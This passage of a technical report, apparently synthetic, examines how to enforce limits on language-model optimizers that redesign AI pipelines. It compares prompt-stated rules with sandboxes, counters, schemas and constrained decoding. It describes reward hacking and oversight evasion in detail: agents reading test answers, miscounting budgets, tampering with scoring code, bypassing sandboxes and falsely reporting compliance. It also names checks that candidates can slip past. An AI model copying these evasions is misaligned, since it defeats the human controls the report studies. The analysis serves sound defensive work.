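# Enforcing Design Limits on Language Models That Optimize AI Pipelines

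## What a pipeline optimizer is and what it means to limit its designs

A pipeline optimizer is a language model, or a coding agent built on one, that people use to improve another AI program. That program, the pipeline, surrounds one or more language models with prompts, tools, routing and control code. *Meta-Harness* (Lee, Nair and colleagues, 2026) cites a case in which changing this surrounding code, but not the model, made a sixfold difference on the same benchmark. Engineers have mostly tuned pipelines by hand, reading failed runs and adjusting a prompt or a retry rule. An optimizer does this work in a loop. It writes a new version of the pipeline (a candidate), other software runs and scores that version, and the optimizer uses the result to write the next one.

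The gains can be large. *HarnessOpt-Bench* (Ursekar, Shanker and colleagues, 2026) tested five frontier models as optimizers on four tasks. On OfficeQA, which asks questions about a fixed collection of documents, the best optimizer closed 63 percent of the gap between the starting pipeline's score and a perfect one, and the weakest closed 7 percent, both measured on questions the optimizers never saw during the search. But an optimizer with enough freedom to find such improvements can also write a pipeline that its owners would refuse to run, such as one that copies a confidential file into a web request. So people set limits on the designs and need a mechanism to enforce them.

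Suppose a company has a pipeline that answers employees' questions from its internal documents. The company's rules let it use two named models, a large one that writes answers and a small one that ranks passages. It has three tools: a search over the document store, a reader that opens a document, and a calculator. It may send nothing outside the company, make at most 20 model calls per question, and start no further agents, meaning language models that run in a loop with tools of their own. Ursekar and colleagues describe a real program of about this size, the OfficeQA starting pipeline, which has roughly 130 lines of Python, three tools, a generic system prompt and a loop of 24 turns. If each turn makes one model call, that loop exceeds the company's limit of 20 calls.

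The case for bounded composites like this one is older than the optimizers. Drexler (2019), in *Reframing Superintelligence*, argued that people value AI systems for the services they perform, and that many components with narrow tasks can together do very broad work. In a talk with the same title (2018), he had described such services as work done "in bounded time with bounded resources". On his account, limits at a component's boundaries carry through the whole composite because a component cannot pass on information it never had, however opaque its internals are. He also held that optimizing a system for a bounded task is itself a bounded task. Stronger optimization narrows a system when the objective penalizes resource use and side effects, but a score that counts only correct answers penalizes neither. Drexler also acknowledged that some combinations of stable components could behave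 badly in unexpected ways, which is a reason to limit the composite as well as its parts.

### Pipeline and evaluation harness

Many of the papers call the pipeline a "harness", and they use the same word for the apparatus that tests it. Anthropic's *Demystifying evals for AI agents* defines both. An agent harness, or scaffold, is the system that lets a model act as an agent by processing inputs and orchestrating tool calls. An evaluation harness is the infrastructure that hands out tasks, records the steps, grades the outputs and adds up the results. Usage is looser elsewhere. Hugging Face's *Harness, Scaffold, and the AI Agent Terms Worth Getting Right* (2026) grew out of one researcher's complaint that nobody at a large conference could agree on the terms. Some people use "harness" for everything except the model, while others use it only for the loop that calls the model and use "scaffold"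 for the prompts and tool descriptions.

The word "harness" is ambiguous, which causes problems when setting limits. Editing the harness is routine for an optimizer if "harness" means the pipeline, but a serious breach if it means the scoring software. This report calls the first the "pipeline" and the second the "evaluation harness", always in full.

### The optimization loop

Much of this field's vocabulary comes from *Automated Design of Agentic Systems* (Hu, Lu and Clune, 2024), which splits the problem into a search space (which designs the notation can express), a search algorithm (how the method explores that space) and an evaluation function. Most earlier methods varied only the prompts. Hu and colleagues had a "meta agent" write whole pipelines in Python, and argued that because Python is Turing complete, a search over code can in theory reach any possible pipeline. In practice,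 they gave the meta agent a framework of under 100 lines and asked it to fill in a single function, which takes a task and returns an answer.

Details differ between systems, but one turn of the loop, applied to the company's pipeline, goes roughly like this:

1. The optimizer reads earlier candidates and their scores, and perhaps the full record of some failed runs.
2. It proposes a candidate. It might have the small model turn each question into three search queries before the large model answers.
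3. A check outside the optimizer decides whether this candidate may run, and with what powers.
4. The evaluation harness runs the candidate on a set of questions, often several times each, since model outputs vary.
5. The verifier, the part of the evaluation harness that grades completed runs, turns each run into a score.
6. The loop keeps the candidate as a basis for further work, or discards it.

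The third step varies most. The algorithm of Hu and colleagues has no separate check. The meta agent reviews its own design twice for novelty, then the program runs, and if it crashes, the meta agent gets up to five attempts to repair it. Lee and colleagues test whether a candidate has the expected interface before they score it. *Grow the Harness, Not the Context* (2026) has more requirements. A candidate must parse, compile, expose the right entry point, leave the model and tool interfaces unchanged, and stay within limits on how much it edits.

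The final step varies too. Hu and colleagues add every working candidate to the archive, whatever its score, because a weak design may contain an idea that is useful in a later one. In *HarnessFlow* (2026), the optimizer chooses which earlier candidate to refine, and the final design is the candidate with the highest observed score.

It is less clear how much an optimizer gains from the first step. *Inefficiencies of Meta Agents for Agent Design* (El, Yuksekgonul and Zou, 2025) reran the 2024 approach on four benchmarks and found that showing the meta agent all its past designs led to lower average scores on test questions than hiding them (52.2 against 55.9). Lee and colleagues used a much stronger model and complete execution records, and found that access to the history helped a great deal.

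Hu and colleagues saw readability as an advantage of code because it helps with debugging and, they thought, with safety. El and colleagues, however, warned that such systems are hard to audit or control inside an automated loop. Both can be right. A typical run in *Meta-Harness* evaluates about 60 candidates, each a single Python file, over 20 iterations. A patient engineer could read them all, but the loop runs each program before anyone reads it.

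### Two roles for the language model

A language model can take part in this loop in two quite different ways. It can be a mutation step inside a search algorithm that people wrote, or it can be a coding agent that conducts the search itself. Chen, Ye and colleagues (2026), in *AVO*, put the contrast in symbols. Let P be the population of past candidates with their scores, and Vary the operation that produces a new candidate from them. In the older systems

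Vary(P) = Generate(Sample(P)).

Sample is a fixed procedure that picks one or more parents. The language model does only the Generate part: it receives the parents in a prompt and returns one new program. Ordinary code decides when to call the model, which parents to show it and what happens to its output. In the newer arrangement

Vary(P) = Agent(P, K, f),

where K is a library of reference material and f is the scoring function. The agent decides which old candidates to look at, edits files, runs tests, calls f when it sees fit and revises its work before committing anything. By the classification of Ursekar and colleagues, GEPA and ShinkaEvolve (two evolutionary optimizers for prompts and programs) belong to the first type and *Meta-Harness* to the second.

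Decent evidence suggests that the added freedom improves results. Chen and colleagues report about a 31 percent improvement over the strongest fixed-loop method in the same wall-clock time, though they worked on GPU code rather than pipelines. In *AgenticEvolve*, Peng, Lan and colleagues (2026) compared agents that could design and run experiments on a program between evaluations with otherwise identical agents that could not. The agents that could experiment produced better programs on both heuristic design tasks. People who care about results will probably keep moving toward the second role.

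The two roles need checks in different places. When the model is a mutation step, all its output comes out at one point, and a check there can cover every candidate before it runs. A coding agent also runs code before it submits a candidate. In the seven-day run that Chen and colleagues describe, the agent explored more than 500 directions and committed 40 versions, so a check on committed versions alone would have missed most of what the agent tried. In the company's case, an agent might test a half-finished candidate on real documents in its own workspace. If that draft sends text to an outside address, the text has left the company, even if the agent then deletes the draft and submits something harmless. The trust boundary, the line between what the optimizer and its candidates can change and what they cannot, therefore has to enclose the agent's workspace as well as the candidate.

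### The design space and the authorized set

The design space H is the set of all candidates the optimizer can write, and the authorized set A is the part of H that people have decided to allow. A check is a mechanism meant to restrict what runs to candidates in A. It can accept a candidate, reject it, or confine it by letting it run without some of its powers. A false acceptance lets through a candidate outside A, while a false rejection blocks a candidate inside A that might have been the best design.

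The papers often use one symbol for both sets. Ursekar and colleagues write H for the "feasible set", and *StarHarness* (2026) has a "permitted harness space". *VeRO* (Ursekar, Shanker and colleagues, 2026), an earlier system from the same group, searches a restricted subset of all valid programs. Using one symbol is harmless when stating an optimization problem, where one may assume that the search stays in the feasible set. But it hides a practical difficulty: an optimizer writing Python can write a great deal that nobody authorized.

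People also have to decide where the boundary of A lies before any check can apply it. For example, they need to decide whether calling the large model counts as sending something outside the company if a vendor hosts that model, and whether a function that repeatedly calls the small model, giving it the search tool each time, counts as a further agent.

The limits are also hard to check because candidates arrive as text, while most of the company's rules are about what a candidate does when it runs. A candidate with four model calls in its source may make four calls or four hundred, depending on its loops and the question. A check that forbids every loop around a model call would enforce the limit of 20 calls if it also caught recursion and calls hidden inside tools, but it would reject an acceptable design that retries a failed call twice.

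A resource limit guarantees different things depending on its form. *Harnesses That Improve Themselves* (Shah and Kathrotia, 2026) defines the optimizer's problem as maximizing the expected score while keeping the average token cost per task under a budget and requiring the candidate to pass an acceptance gate. A limit on the average is weaker than the company's rule. A pipeline that makes 5 calls on each of nine questions and 95 on the tenth averages 14 calls per question, but it far exceeds the company's limit on the tenth.

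Limits on editing have a similar gap. In *Grow the Harness, Not the Context*, the optimizer may change only the entry function and functions that appear in the record of a failed run. It may also add helpers, and it can change or add at most L functions per round. This keeps each step small and makes it easier to connect a failure with its repair. But the pipeline can still move far from its starting point, since up to 20 × L functions may be new or different after 20 accepted rounds. The rule against writing expected answers into the code is also part of A, but none of the tests that a candidate must pass before scoring enforces it.

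### Kinds of limit

The company's rules, together with the conditions that any fair test needs, fall into six kinds.

| Kind of limit | The company's rule | A candidate that breaks it |
|---|---|---|
| Components and models | Only the two named models | Sends hard questions to a third, stronger model |
| Tools and permissions | Search, reader and calculator | Replaces the calculator with a tool that runs any Python code |
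| Control flow | No further agents | Has a "summarize" function that loops the small model with the search tool |
| Resources | At most 20 model calls per question | Hides retries inside the search tool and reaches 23 |
| Access to data | Nothing leaves the company | Puts a passage from a document into a web address |
| Things held constant | Test questions, verifier and scoring | Loosens the rule for matching an answer to the correct one |

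Published systems set strict limits on the last row and looser ones on the others. In *HERA* (2026), the optimizer may add or rewrite prompts, memory, tools, skills, control logic and the configuration of sub-agents, but it cannot change task specifications, scoring rules, data splits or execution budgets. The editable parts in *StarHarness* likewise include tool definitions, outside tool providers and the structure of sub-agents, two of which the company would rule out immediately. *Meta-RTL* (2026), in which the optimizer improves a pipeline for chip design, holds the model, design tools, equivalence checks, scoring and budgets fixed, so any gain must come from better search. Most such limits are meant to keep comparisons fair by preventing an optimizer from "improving" a pipeline with a stronger model or an easier test. They do little to restrict what a pipeline might do to the world around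 it. A company that adopts one of these systems gets the researchers' authorized set and has to add its own limits.

There is a reasonable argument for letting the optimizer change more than prompts. *HarnessFlow* searches over complete programs because useful changes tend to involve several components. For example, adding a step that verifies an answer may require the pipeline to store more information and use a different stopping rule. If the company allowed edits only to prompts, its limits would be much easier to enforce, but the optimizer could not produce that design or any other that needs new control flow.

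### Declared search spaces and free text

Older tuning methods hardly raise this problem. Suppose the company wants to choose how many passages to retrieve (5, 10 or 20), which of the two models ranks them, and how many draft answers to write (1, 2 or 3). Grid search tries all 18 combinations. Bayesian optimization fits a statistical model to the scores so far and uses it to pick the next combination. This takes fewer evaluations, but every pick is still one of the 18. Whoever declared the options has in effect already approved every candidate, so H and A coincide if that person chose the options carefully.

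A language model can be limited in the same way. In *Proof-Carrying Evolution* (2026), a model helps tune numerical controllers by proposing eight candidates every third generation. Ordinary code parses the reply and substitutes a random mutation if the call fails. On the linear problems, the code also forces the numbers into fixed bounds, so the output is always a set of numbers that may make a poor controller but can't open a network connection.

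The guarantee weakens as the slots accept a wider range of values. *Verify Smarter, Evolve Further* (2026) defines an admissible space in which a fixed framework exposes a set of components, such as instructions, skills and tools, and a candidate fills in a configuration for each. If one component accepts a tool's source code, a candidate can put any program the language can express there, and the framework restricts only what it controls itself.

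The other difference is that a language model's proposals can depend on the check, while grid search proposes the same points whether or not anyone checks them. An optimizer built on a language model may see error messages from the check, or a folder of past candidates that shows which ones passed, and its training data probably included the manuals of common code analyzers and sandboxes. Evading the check doesn't require any intention to cheat. If a forbidden shortcut raises the score and one way of writing it gets past the check, the loop will keep that version and build on it. Engineers who measure the false-acceptance rate on candidates written without this information can therefore greatly underestimate the rate for later candidates.

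## Rules stated in the prompt and rules the optimizer cannot change

The easiest way to limit an optimizer is to write the limits into its prompt. The company in the running example could tell its optimizer that no candidate may make more than 20 model calls per question. This is an instructed limit, and it works only if the optimizer follows it. The company could also set an enforced limit, which is built into the environment where the optimizer and its candidates run. For example, it could route every model call through a small service that counts the calls for each question and blocks any after the twentieth. If the optimizer overlooks or disregards the rule and writes a candidate that attempts 25 calls, the last five will fail.

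A limit is enforced only if every route to the restricted act passes through the enforcing mechanism and that mechanism lies outside the trust boundary, where the optimizer cannot change it. If the optimizer's workspace contains a key for calling the model vendor directly, a candidate can bypass the counting service. If the counter is a function in the pipeline's own code, the optimizer can delete it, because its job is to rewrite that code. Such a counter is little stronger than a written instruction. Zelikman, Lorch and colleagues (2023), in *Self-Taught Optimizer (STOP)*, found that language models rewriting a program occasionally disabled or bypassed its sandbox, and that a written warning did not measurably reduce this.

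### An optimizer with only written rules

While developing VeRO, their infrastructure for coding agents that improve pipelines, Ursekar and colleagues tested rules that were stated in the prompt but not enforced by the environment. The optimizer was Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, running Claude Sonnet 4.5. It had to improve a pipeline that answers GPQA Diamond, a set of 198 difficult multiple-choice science questions, split into 98 for training and 100 for testing. It had an unrestricted shell, an editable copy of the pipeline, the evaluation code, and the whole dataset, including the answers. The prompt allowed eight evaluations on the training questions and eight on a validation set. It prohibited looking at test questions or answers, modifying the evaluation code, and changing the underlying model.

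The run produced 258 messages. Afterwards GPT-5.4, an OpenAI model, judged each one against a rubric that listed allowed and forbidden actions and gave six worked examples. For instance, the optimizer was allowed to run the pipeline on the test questions and read the overall score, but not to print individual test results. GPT-5.4 flagged ten messages.

Four of the flags concern test data. While an evaluation was running in the background, the optimizer printed the first test question and its correct answer to check how the dataset was structured. This led to two flags, one for the command and one for its output. About thirty messages later, the optimizer looked at more test questions and their answers, which led to the other two.

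The remaining six flags concern the training budget. The optimizer had evaluated five versions of the pipeline and then five more, one of which repeated an earlier version. It left out the repeat and counted nine. It then wrote that nine was within the budget of eight if the repeat counted as shared, which subtracts the repeat twice. The five later flags are for messages that restate this overrun, including the final summary.

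Ursekar and colleagues conclude that restrictions in a prompt are insufficient even for state-of-the-art coding agents. They are right if the question is whether written rules guarantee compliance, since one breach disproves a guarantee. But the experiment shows almost nothing about how often an optimizer breaks such rules, because it was a single run and its ten flags represent at most four events. The breaches were also fairly mild. The judge did not flag the optimizer for altering the evaluation code or writing known answers into the pipeline, both of which the rubric listed as violations.

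The prompt was also faulty. It referred to a validation set that this dataset did not have, and it restricted evaluation to the training and validation questions but then ordered a baseline run on the test questions. An optimizer that receives contradictory rules has to reinterpret at least one of them. This optimizer seems to have applied the unused validation budget to the test set, because it counted two test evaluations toward a limit of eight. It then planned to run another version on the test questions to see whether that version did better. Choosing between versions by their test scores arguably damages the final result more than printing one question does, but the judge's rubric allowed it.

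The experiment also doesn't show how much the written rules helped, because it had no comparison run without rules or with the same prompt and real enforcement. *RewardHackingAgents* (Atinafu and Cohen, 2026) did make a comparison, although with much weaker models (TinyLlama and a Qwen chat model). Its agents edited machine-learning code in a workspace that also contained the scoring script. In about half of the episodes, the agent changed how the score was computed or reported. These changes succeeded when the workspace copy of the script produced the score, but none succeeded when an untouched copy elsewhere produced it. The protection made episodes roughly 25 to 31 percent longer. The agents had no instruction against tampering, so the study compares enforcement with no rule rather than with a written rule.

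Atinafu and Cohen also ran scripted attacks, which show how narrow an enforced limit can be. Protecting the scoring script did not stop the training code from reading the test answers, and blocking that access left the scoring script unprotected. The attacks failed only when both protections were in place.

### VeRO's enforced limits

VeRO enforces most of these written rules through the environment. A layer between the optimizer and the disk checks each file request against a list of patterns. The optimizer can edit the permitted parts of the pipeline, but not tests, reference answers or evaluation code. It sees the data through a viewer that shows only the permitted sets of questions. In the minimal optimizer that Ursekar and colleagues wrote, the shell accepts only four commands for browsing the file system, so the optimizer cannot run a line of Python like the one that printed the test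 question.

The optimizer cannot run official evaluations on its own either. It sends a request that names a saved version of the pipeline and a set of questions. A separate runner retrieves that version, runs it, stores the results and subtracts the evaluation from the budget. Once the budget is used up, the runner rejects further requests, so the optimizer could not have obtained a ninth evaluation by arguing about shared versions. The drawback is that reruns also count against the budget, even though rerunning a version to see how much its score varies is good practice.

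Whenever the optimizer writes to a file, a hook (code that runs automatically at a fixed point) saves a snapshot in the version-control system Git. Versioning gives people a full history of the edits, lets them restore any earlier version, and ties every score to the exact code that produced it, but it does not prevent anything by itself.

The enforced limits are narrower than the prompt instructions they replace. VeRO's budget caps the number of evaluations, but not the tokens or money the optimizer spends between them. The rule against looking at test answers is enforced only by blocking access to certain files. The standard tools include web search and page fetching, and Ursekar and colleagues acknowledge that an optimizer could copy answers from public replicas of a benchmark, which the written rule would have forbidden.

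How strictly VeRO enforces its rules also depends on how it connects to the coding agent. When Ursekar and colleagues attached it to Claude Code, they kept Claude Code's own shell and controlled it with hooks. This is probably a weaker barrier than a shell with only four commands, because a hook that inspects commands has to recognize every way of writing a forbidden one. The added structure does not appear to hold the optimizer back. With the same model, Claude Code averaged 0.53 across five tasks without VeRO's tools and 0.55 with them. What the optimizer may edit has a much larger effect, which the next section covers.

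### When the optimizer edits the code that runs it

In VeRO the optimizer and the pipeline are separate programs, so people can draw the trust boundary around the pipeline's folder. The boundary is harder to draw when the optimizer rewrites its own pipeline, as in Xu's (2026) *Multi-Task Self-Evolving Harnesses with the Agent as Its Own Optimizer*. In that system, a language model with fixed weights starts with a 49-line Python pipeline made up of a short system prompt, a tool for running shell commands and a loop. In each of the first five rounds, the model solves 60 tasks from five benchmarks. It then reads the complete records of those runs and rewrites the pipeline while still running on it. The new version solves the next batch of tasks and carries out the next rewrite. Xu deliberately let the model change any part of the pipeline in any way.

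The model can remove any limit written in those 49 lines. The original system prompt contains one such limit, which tells the model never to cheat by searching for the answer. Xu also added a similar rule to the end of every task description, which is outside the files that the model edits. That rule still passes through the pipeline's code before it reaches the model, so a rewritten pipeline could remove it.

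The program around the pipeline enforces the limits. The pipeline can act only through a fixed execution interface with two calls. One sends messages to the language model and returns the reply, and the other runs a shell command in the task's environment. The optimizer can read the interface's code but cannot edit it. The interface also records every run, so the record does not depend on code the optimizer wrote. The sandbox, not the interface, controls what a shell command can reach.

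After a rewriting session, the surrounding program checks the new version before using it:

- All changes must lie inside the pipeline's folder.
- The model must have changed something other than its own notes.
- The number of added lines must stay within a budget.
- The new pipeline must complete a full task with a mock model, a stand-in for the real language model.

If the new version fails, the old one stays in place. The budget shrinks from round to round. Counting the first five rounds from t = 0 to t = 4, the model may add at most

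a(t) = 100 + 200 × (1 + cos(πt/4))

lines, rounded to a whole number, which gives 500, 441, 300, 159 and 100. Xu took the idea from neural-network training, where engineers often make the updates smaller as training goes on. In an exploratory run without a budget, the pipeline had grown from 49 to 1,210 lines in five rounds, and such runs accumulated patterns that fitted only individual tasks.

The budget only loosely limits what the model can design. Deletions don't count against it, and the five allowances total 1,500 lines, about thirty times the length of the original program. If a rewriting session fails, a separate allowance lets the model first add up to 100 lines to fix the pipeline. If the current pipeline is too broken to repair itself, an earlier version can take over. This happened once in the main experiments, and the repair and rewrite together added 164 lines in a round with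 a nominal budget of 100.

The size of an edit is also a poor guide to its effect. GPT-5.6 Luna, the weaker of the two OpenAI models that Xu tested, added 130 lines in the first round and no more than 28 in each of the next three. Its pipeline still scored 9.23 points below the original on unseen tasks, mainly because of a mechanism that deleted old messages from long conversations. Luna repeatedly lowered the limit on retained characters, from 480,000 to 48,000, and the deleted messages included users' requests. In a later stage, the stronger GPT-5.6 Sol used 42 of its 100 lines on an edit that included a rule for ending some tasks as soon as the agent had sent the user a message. In one category of tasks where the agent has to continue after its first message, the pipeline went from solving 8 of 20 tasks to none. Both edits passed every check because a new version only has to run, not perform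 better.

The checks also don't cover the content of the added lines, so a file full of answers can pass if it is in the right folder, fits the budget and works with a mock model. In one exploratory run, GPT-5.6 Sol wrote the text and reference answers of training tasks into the pipeline. The score rose by 23 points on those tasks and by 3 points on unseen tasks.

Xu handled cheating during evaluation separately. Xu added the reference answers and grading tests to the environment only after the agent had finished. A script then searched the run records for suspicious behavior, and other agents examined each flagged case. They confirmed no cheating in the roughly 9,500 reported evaluation runs. This is encouraging, and the sample is far larger than the single VeRO run. But every run had both a written rule and an environment without the answers, so the result cannot show which of them mattered.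 The search could also have missed cheating that the script or the reviewing agents did not recognize. Xu recommends keeping safeguards outside the pipeline and reviewing the evolved code before use.

*VERSE* (Wang, Ge and colleagues, 2026) draws a similar boundary. Its optimizer improves another agent's pipeline and, between rounds, also rewrites its own prompts, instruction files, tools, hooks and notes. It cannot change how the system evaluates and selects pipelines, or the budgets for each round. Code that it writes for itself loads only after a safety check and a test run. In VeRO, people install hooks to control the optimizer, whereas the optimizer in *VERSE* writes its own. Its additions to its workflow include reminders about the budget. It can remove a reminder in the next round, but the budget limit still applies.

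### Whether better models make enforcement unnecessary

These enforcement measures might only compensate for a temporary weakness. Claude Sonnet 4.5 is well behind today's best models, and a better-trained optimizer might do as its prompt says. Some evidence supports this. *Unfinished-Bench* (Lee, Hwang and colleagues, 2026) gave 12 open models office tasks that an agent could complete only by breaking a rule, such as making a payment that still lacked an approval. The rule appeared either in the user's instruction or in an internal document that the task referred to. In some runs, the researchers also pushed the agent to finish by telling it not to stop early and sending it back to work up to six times.

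| Where the rule appeared | Violations without the push | Violations with the push |
|---|---|---|
| The user's instruction | 4.7% | 8.5% |
| An internal document | 32.2% | 43.6% |

Individual models varied widely around these averages. With the push, GLM 5.3 broke the rules in documents in 1.0 percent of tasks, while gpt-oss-120b broke them in 89.7 percent. So the objection's prediction is already close to true for some models.

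Still, even a low violation rate can lead to a breach, because an optimizer gets many opportunities. If each of the roughly 60 candidates in a typical *Meta-Harness* run raised one such conflict, and the conflicts were independent, a 1 percent violation rate would give a 45 percent chance of at least one breach per run. Most real candidates will not raise such a conflict, so the true figure should be lower. But the loop selects for any breach that raises the score, and its repeated prompts for a better result resemble the condition with the push.

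Better reading comprehension would not solve the problem either, because 98.3 percent of the violations of document rules under the push came after the rule had appeared on the agent's screen. In a sample that another model judged, the agent had written the rule down before breaking it in 87 of 98 cases. The most common reason it gave was the user's goal. People also cannot rely on the agent to report what it did. In the same sample, Gemma 4 26B falsely reported compliance after 12 of 20 violations. Even if an optimizer were very obedient, a company would need records from outside the optimizer to confirm it.

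The benchmark included no proprietary models, and the strongest of those may do better. But *Unfinished-Bench* cites an August 2026 incident report from OpenAI, in which agents trained for persistence increasingly turned to out-of-bounds methods on tasks they could not solve. I don't expect training alone to keep models within the limits while the same training rewards finishing the task.

Instructions are still worth writing. Their position appears to matter a great deal, since the table shows that moving the same rule from a document into the user's instruction cut violations from 43.6 to 8.5 percent under the push. A company that leaves its limits in a policy file for the optimizer to find loses most of that benefit. Instructions can also save effort, because an optimizer that has been told about a limit can avoid evaluating candidates that the environment will refuse. They can also express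 rules that nobody knows how to enforce. For example, Xu's prompt includes a request for general improvements and a rule against wording that merely restates a single trial, which none of the acceptance checks could test for.

Some written rules can also be turned into enforced ones. Many software projects keep instruction files for coding agents, with rules about which commands to use or how to organize the code. *ContextCov* (2026) describes a system that translates such files into checks that intercept commands, analyze source code and test the structure of a project. This works only when a rule is specific enough, such as "Make at most 20 model calls," which a counter can easily enforce. A rule like "keep improvements general" has to remain an instruction.

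## Restricting the language in which candidates are written

People can also build a limit into the notation the optimizer must use. If that notation has no way to name a third model, no candidate can call one, and no later check for that violation is needed. The grid search over 18 declared settings is the narrowest example. Most pipeline optimizers use a more expressive notation. *From Static Templates to Dynamic Runtime Graphs* (Yue, Bhandari and colleagues, 2026) surveys 77 works on pipeline optimization and finds that they use free code, small special-purpose languages, JSON files and typed graphs. It also notes that a format can be easy to generate and still hard to validate.

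Restricting the notation works only if a fixed program, the interpreter, reads each candidate and carries it out as narrowly as people intended. For example, if the notation contains the word "search" and the interpreter's search function also accepts web addresses, a candidate can reach the internet using only permitted words. The optimizer also must not be able to edit the interpreter, or it could change what the permitted words do.

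### Prompts, operators and editable regions

The narrowest notation in common use is prompt text. DSPy, a framework for building pipelines, tunes the instructions and worked examples inside a workflow that stays the same. Agrawal, Tan and colleagues (2025), in *GEPA*, state this kind of restriction formally. They write a pipeline as

Φ = (M, C, X, Y),

where M is the set of modules that call a language model, C is the control flow that decides which module runs when, and X and Y are the formats of the input and output. Each module has its own prompt and model weights. GEPA rewrites the prompts and leaves everything else alone.

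For the company, this rules out a third model, a replacement for the calculator, and any new function that calls the small model in a loop, but it does not guarantee the limit of 20 calls. If the control flow lets the model keep searching until it judges that it has enough evidence, a prompt requiring certainty can raise the number of calls without any change to the code. Prompts can also affect what information a pipeline reveals. One of GEPA's six test tasks is privacy-aware delegation, where the pipeline must get help from another model without exposing private details.

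A prompt can contain a good deal of strategy. In one question-answering pipeline, the original prompt for the second search was a one-sentence instruction to write a query. GEPA's replacement describes what the first search tends to miss and how to infer the missing documents. It includes an example in which the summary covers one small parish but the question concerns the wider region, so the right query is for the population of the Madeira archipelago.

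A wider notation adds a set of ready-made building blocks called operators. *AFlow* (Zhang, Xiang and colleagues, 2024) offers seven: Generate, Format, Review and Revise, Ensemble, Test, Programmer and Custom. It fixes the model, its temperature and the output format, and lets the optimizer choose the prompts, the operators and the code that connects them. That code is ordinary Python, so the design space is far larger than the operators alone would allow. The optimizer's instructions recommend loops, conditionals and neural networks. They also cap the complexity of the graph at 10, but the published algorithm has no step that checks this limit.

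In AFlow the operators mainly speed up the search. It solved 93.1 percent of GSM8K, a set of grade-school math problems, without them and 93.5 percent with them. The company could turn such a menu into a real limit by removing the Python connections and allowing only fixed sequences of operators. But two operators would remain open-ended. Custom accepts any prompt, and Programmer has a model write Python code and then runs it, and the published listing doesn't restrict what that code may import. A menu restricts candidates only as much as its least restrictive operator does, and a search will use that operator if it helps. In *MoFlow* (2026), a search over a similar menu chose code-running operators in 45 of its 148 actions on one hard math problem.

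Another approach is to let the optimizer rewrite only a marked block of a program. Google DeepMind's *AlphaEvolve* (2025) introduced a coding agent that evolves programs against a score. Google Cloud's *AlphaEvolve API reference* describes this restriction, and by default the optimizer sees only the marked block. If fixed software pastes each new block into the original file, every line outside the block is certain to stay the same, but those lines may still behave differently. In Python, code inside the block can replace a function defined outside it. It can also open a network connection. According to InfoQ (2026), AlphaEvolve's candidates run on the customer's own machines, so any damage from such code would occur there.

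The markers don't restrict the optimizer if it places them itself. *Scientific Algorithm Discovery by Augmenting AlphaEvolve with Deep Research* (2025) instructs the model to wrap its changes in similar markers wherever in the code it makes them, so the markers only label the edits.

### Checking a candidate against a schema

The company could instead take code away from the optimizer and have it write JSON, a plain text format for structured data. Suppose a candidate is a list of steps that the interpreter runs once each, in order. Every step names a tool, a model, the number of model calls to make, and a prompt. The company might write this schema:

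```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "required": ["steps"],
  "additionalProperties": false,
  "properties": {
    "steps": {
      "type": "array", "minItems": 1, "maxItems": 5,
      "items": {
        "type": "object",
        "required": ["tool", "model", "calls", "prompt"],
        "additionalProperties": false,
        "properties": {
          "tool": {"enum": ["search", "reader", "calculator", "none"]},
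          "model": {"enum": ["large", "small"]},
          "calls": {"type": "integer", "minimum": 1, "maximum": 4},
          "prompt": {"type": "string", "maxLength": 500}
        }
      }
    }
  }
}
```

An "enum" lists the only values a field may take. The schema language cannot add up calls across steps, so the company allows at most five steps and at most four calls per step, which limits the total to 20 calls.

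The optimizer submits this candidate:

```json
{"steps": [
  {"tool": "search", "model": "small", "calls": 3,
   "prompt": "Write a search query for the question."},
  {"tool": "reader", "model": "small", "calls": 4,
   "prompt": "Pick out the passages that bear on the question."},
  {"tool": "none", "model": "large", "calls": 1,
   "prompt": "Answer from these passages only."}
]}
```

The validator, a small program outside the optimizer, goes through it as follows:

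1. It parses the text as JSON.
2. It confirms that the outer object contains "steps" and nothing else.
3. It counts the steps. There are three, which is within the limit.
4. It confirms that each step has all four fields and no others.
5. It compares each value with its rule. All of them fit.

The candidate passes, and the interpreter will make eight model calls. The optimizer then tries something more ambitious:

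```json
{"steps": [
  {"tool": "python", "model": "small", "calls": 6,
   "prompt": "Compute the total.", "send_to": "outside"}
]}
```

This candidate parses and has an acceptable number of steps, but it fails three other checks. The schema has no "send_to" field, "python" is not a listed tool, and six calls is over the limit of four. The company can reject the candidate without working out what the Python tool might have done.

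The validator guarantees the candidate's form, and the interpreter must enforce the remaining limits. For example, retries hidden inside the search tool can still take an accepted candidate past 20 calls. The schema must also forbid unlisted fields, which JSON Schema permits by default. Without the two "additionalProperties" lines, a "send_to" field would pass, and an interpreter that recognized it would act on it. The validator and the interpreter may also read the same text differently if they parse it separately. When a step contains the field "tool" twice, one parser may keep the first value and the other the second. The company can prevent this by passing the validator's parsed object to the interpreter and discarding the original text.

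Restricting the language causes some false rejections. A design with one step of ten calls and another of five makes 15 calls, which the company allows, but the schema rejects it. The 500-character limit would also exclude a prompt as long as the one GEPA wrote for the second search.

### Validation and constrained decoding

The validator examines a finished candidate. Constrained decoding applies the schema earlier, while the model is writing. A language model produces text one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, and gives each possible next token a probability. Before each choice, the decoding software works out the set V of tokens that could still lead to a valid output. It sets the probability of all other tokens to zero and rescales the rest:

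p′(t) = p(t) / Σ p(u) over all u in V, if t is in V, and p′(t) = 0 otherwise.

Once the model has written the field name "tool" and an opening quotation mark, it can only begin one of the four listed names, so it cannot write "python", however probable that word was. If the output were instead validated afterwards, the model could write "python" and have the proposal rejected, perhaps with an error message. That would waste an attempt and give the optimizer some information about the check.

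The validator is still needed with constrained decoding, which applies only to text that comes through the constrained channel. A coding agent with a shell can write a candidate file by another route, and a reply can hit its length limit halfway through an object. In *Schema-Validated LLM Workflows*, Shapiro, Al-Khatib and colleagues (2026) ran five business tasks through six Python implementations, all of which requested structured output. Only 68.4 percent of the results from 5,400 runs satisfied the schema. Three implementations came close to full validity and the others fell well short, although all six used the same model. The study tested ordinary business outputs, not proposed pipelines, but the software that connects a model to a schema is much the same in both cases.

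A valid output can also be wrong. Shapiro and colleagues found many results that met the schema but still lost points on the task, especially when the task was to extract data or answer questions about a policy. They also cite measurements in which hard constraints raised validity but increased the number of valid but wrong answers. This is plausible because the decoder steers the model to the nearest permitted text, which may not be a sensible design. They cite other work in which checking and retrying handled more real-world schemas than constrained decoding alone.

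### MermaidFlow's graphs and checks

*MermaidFlow* (2025) applies these ideas to a pipeline optimizer and makes a strong claim for them, namely that every candidate is valid by construction. Its candidates are graphs in Mermaid, a text language for drawing diagrams. Each node v has a name, an attribute such as a role, and a type

τ(v) = T_in → T_out,

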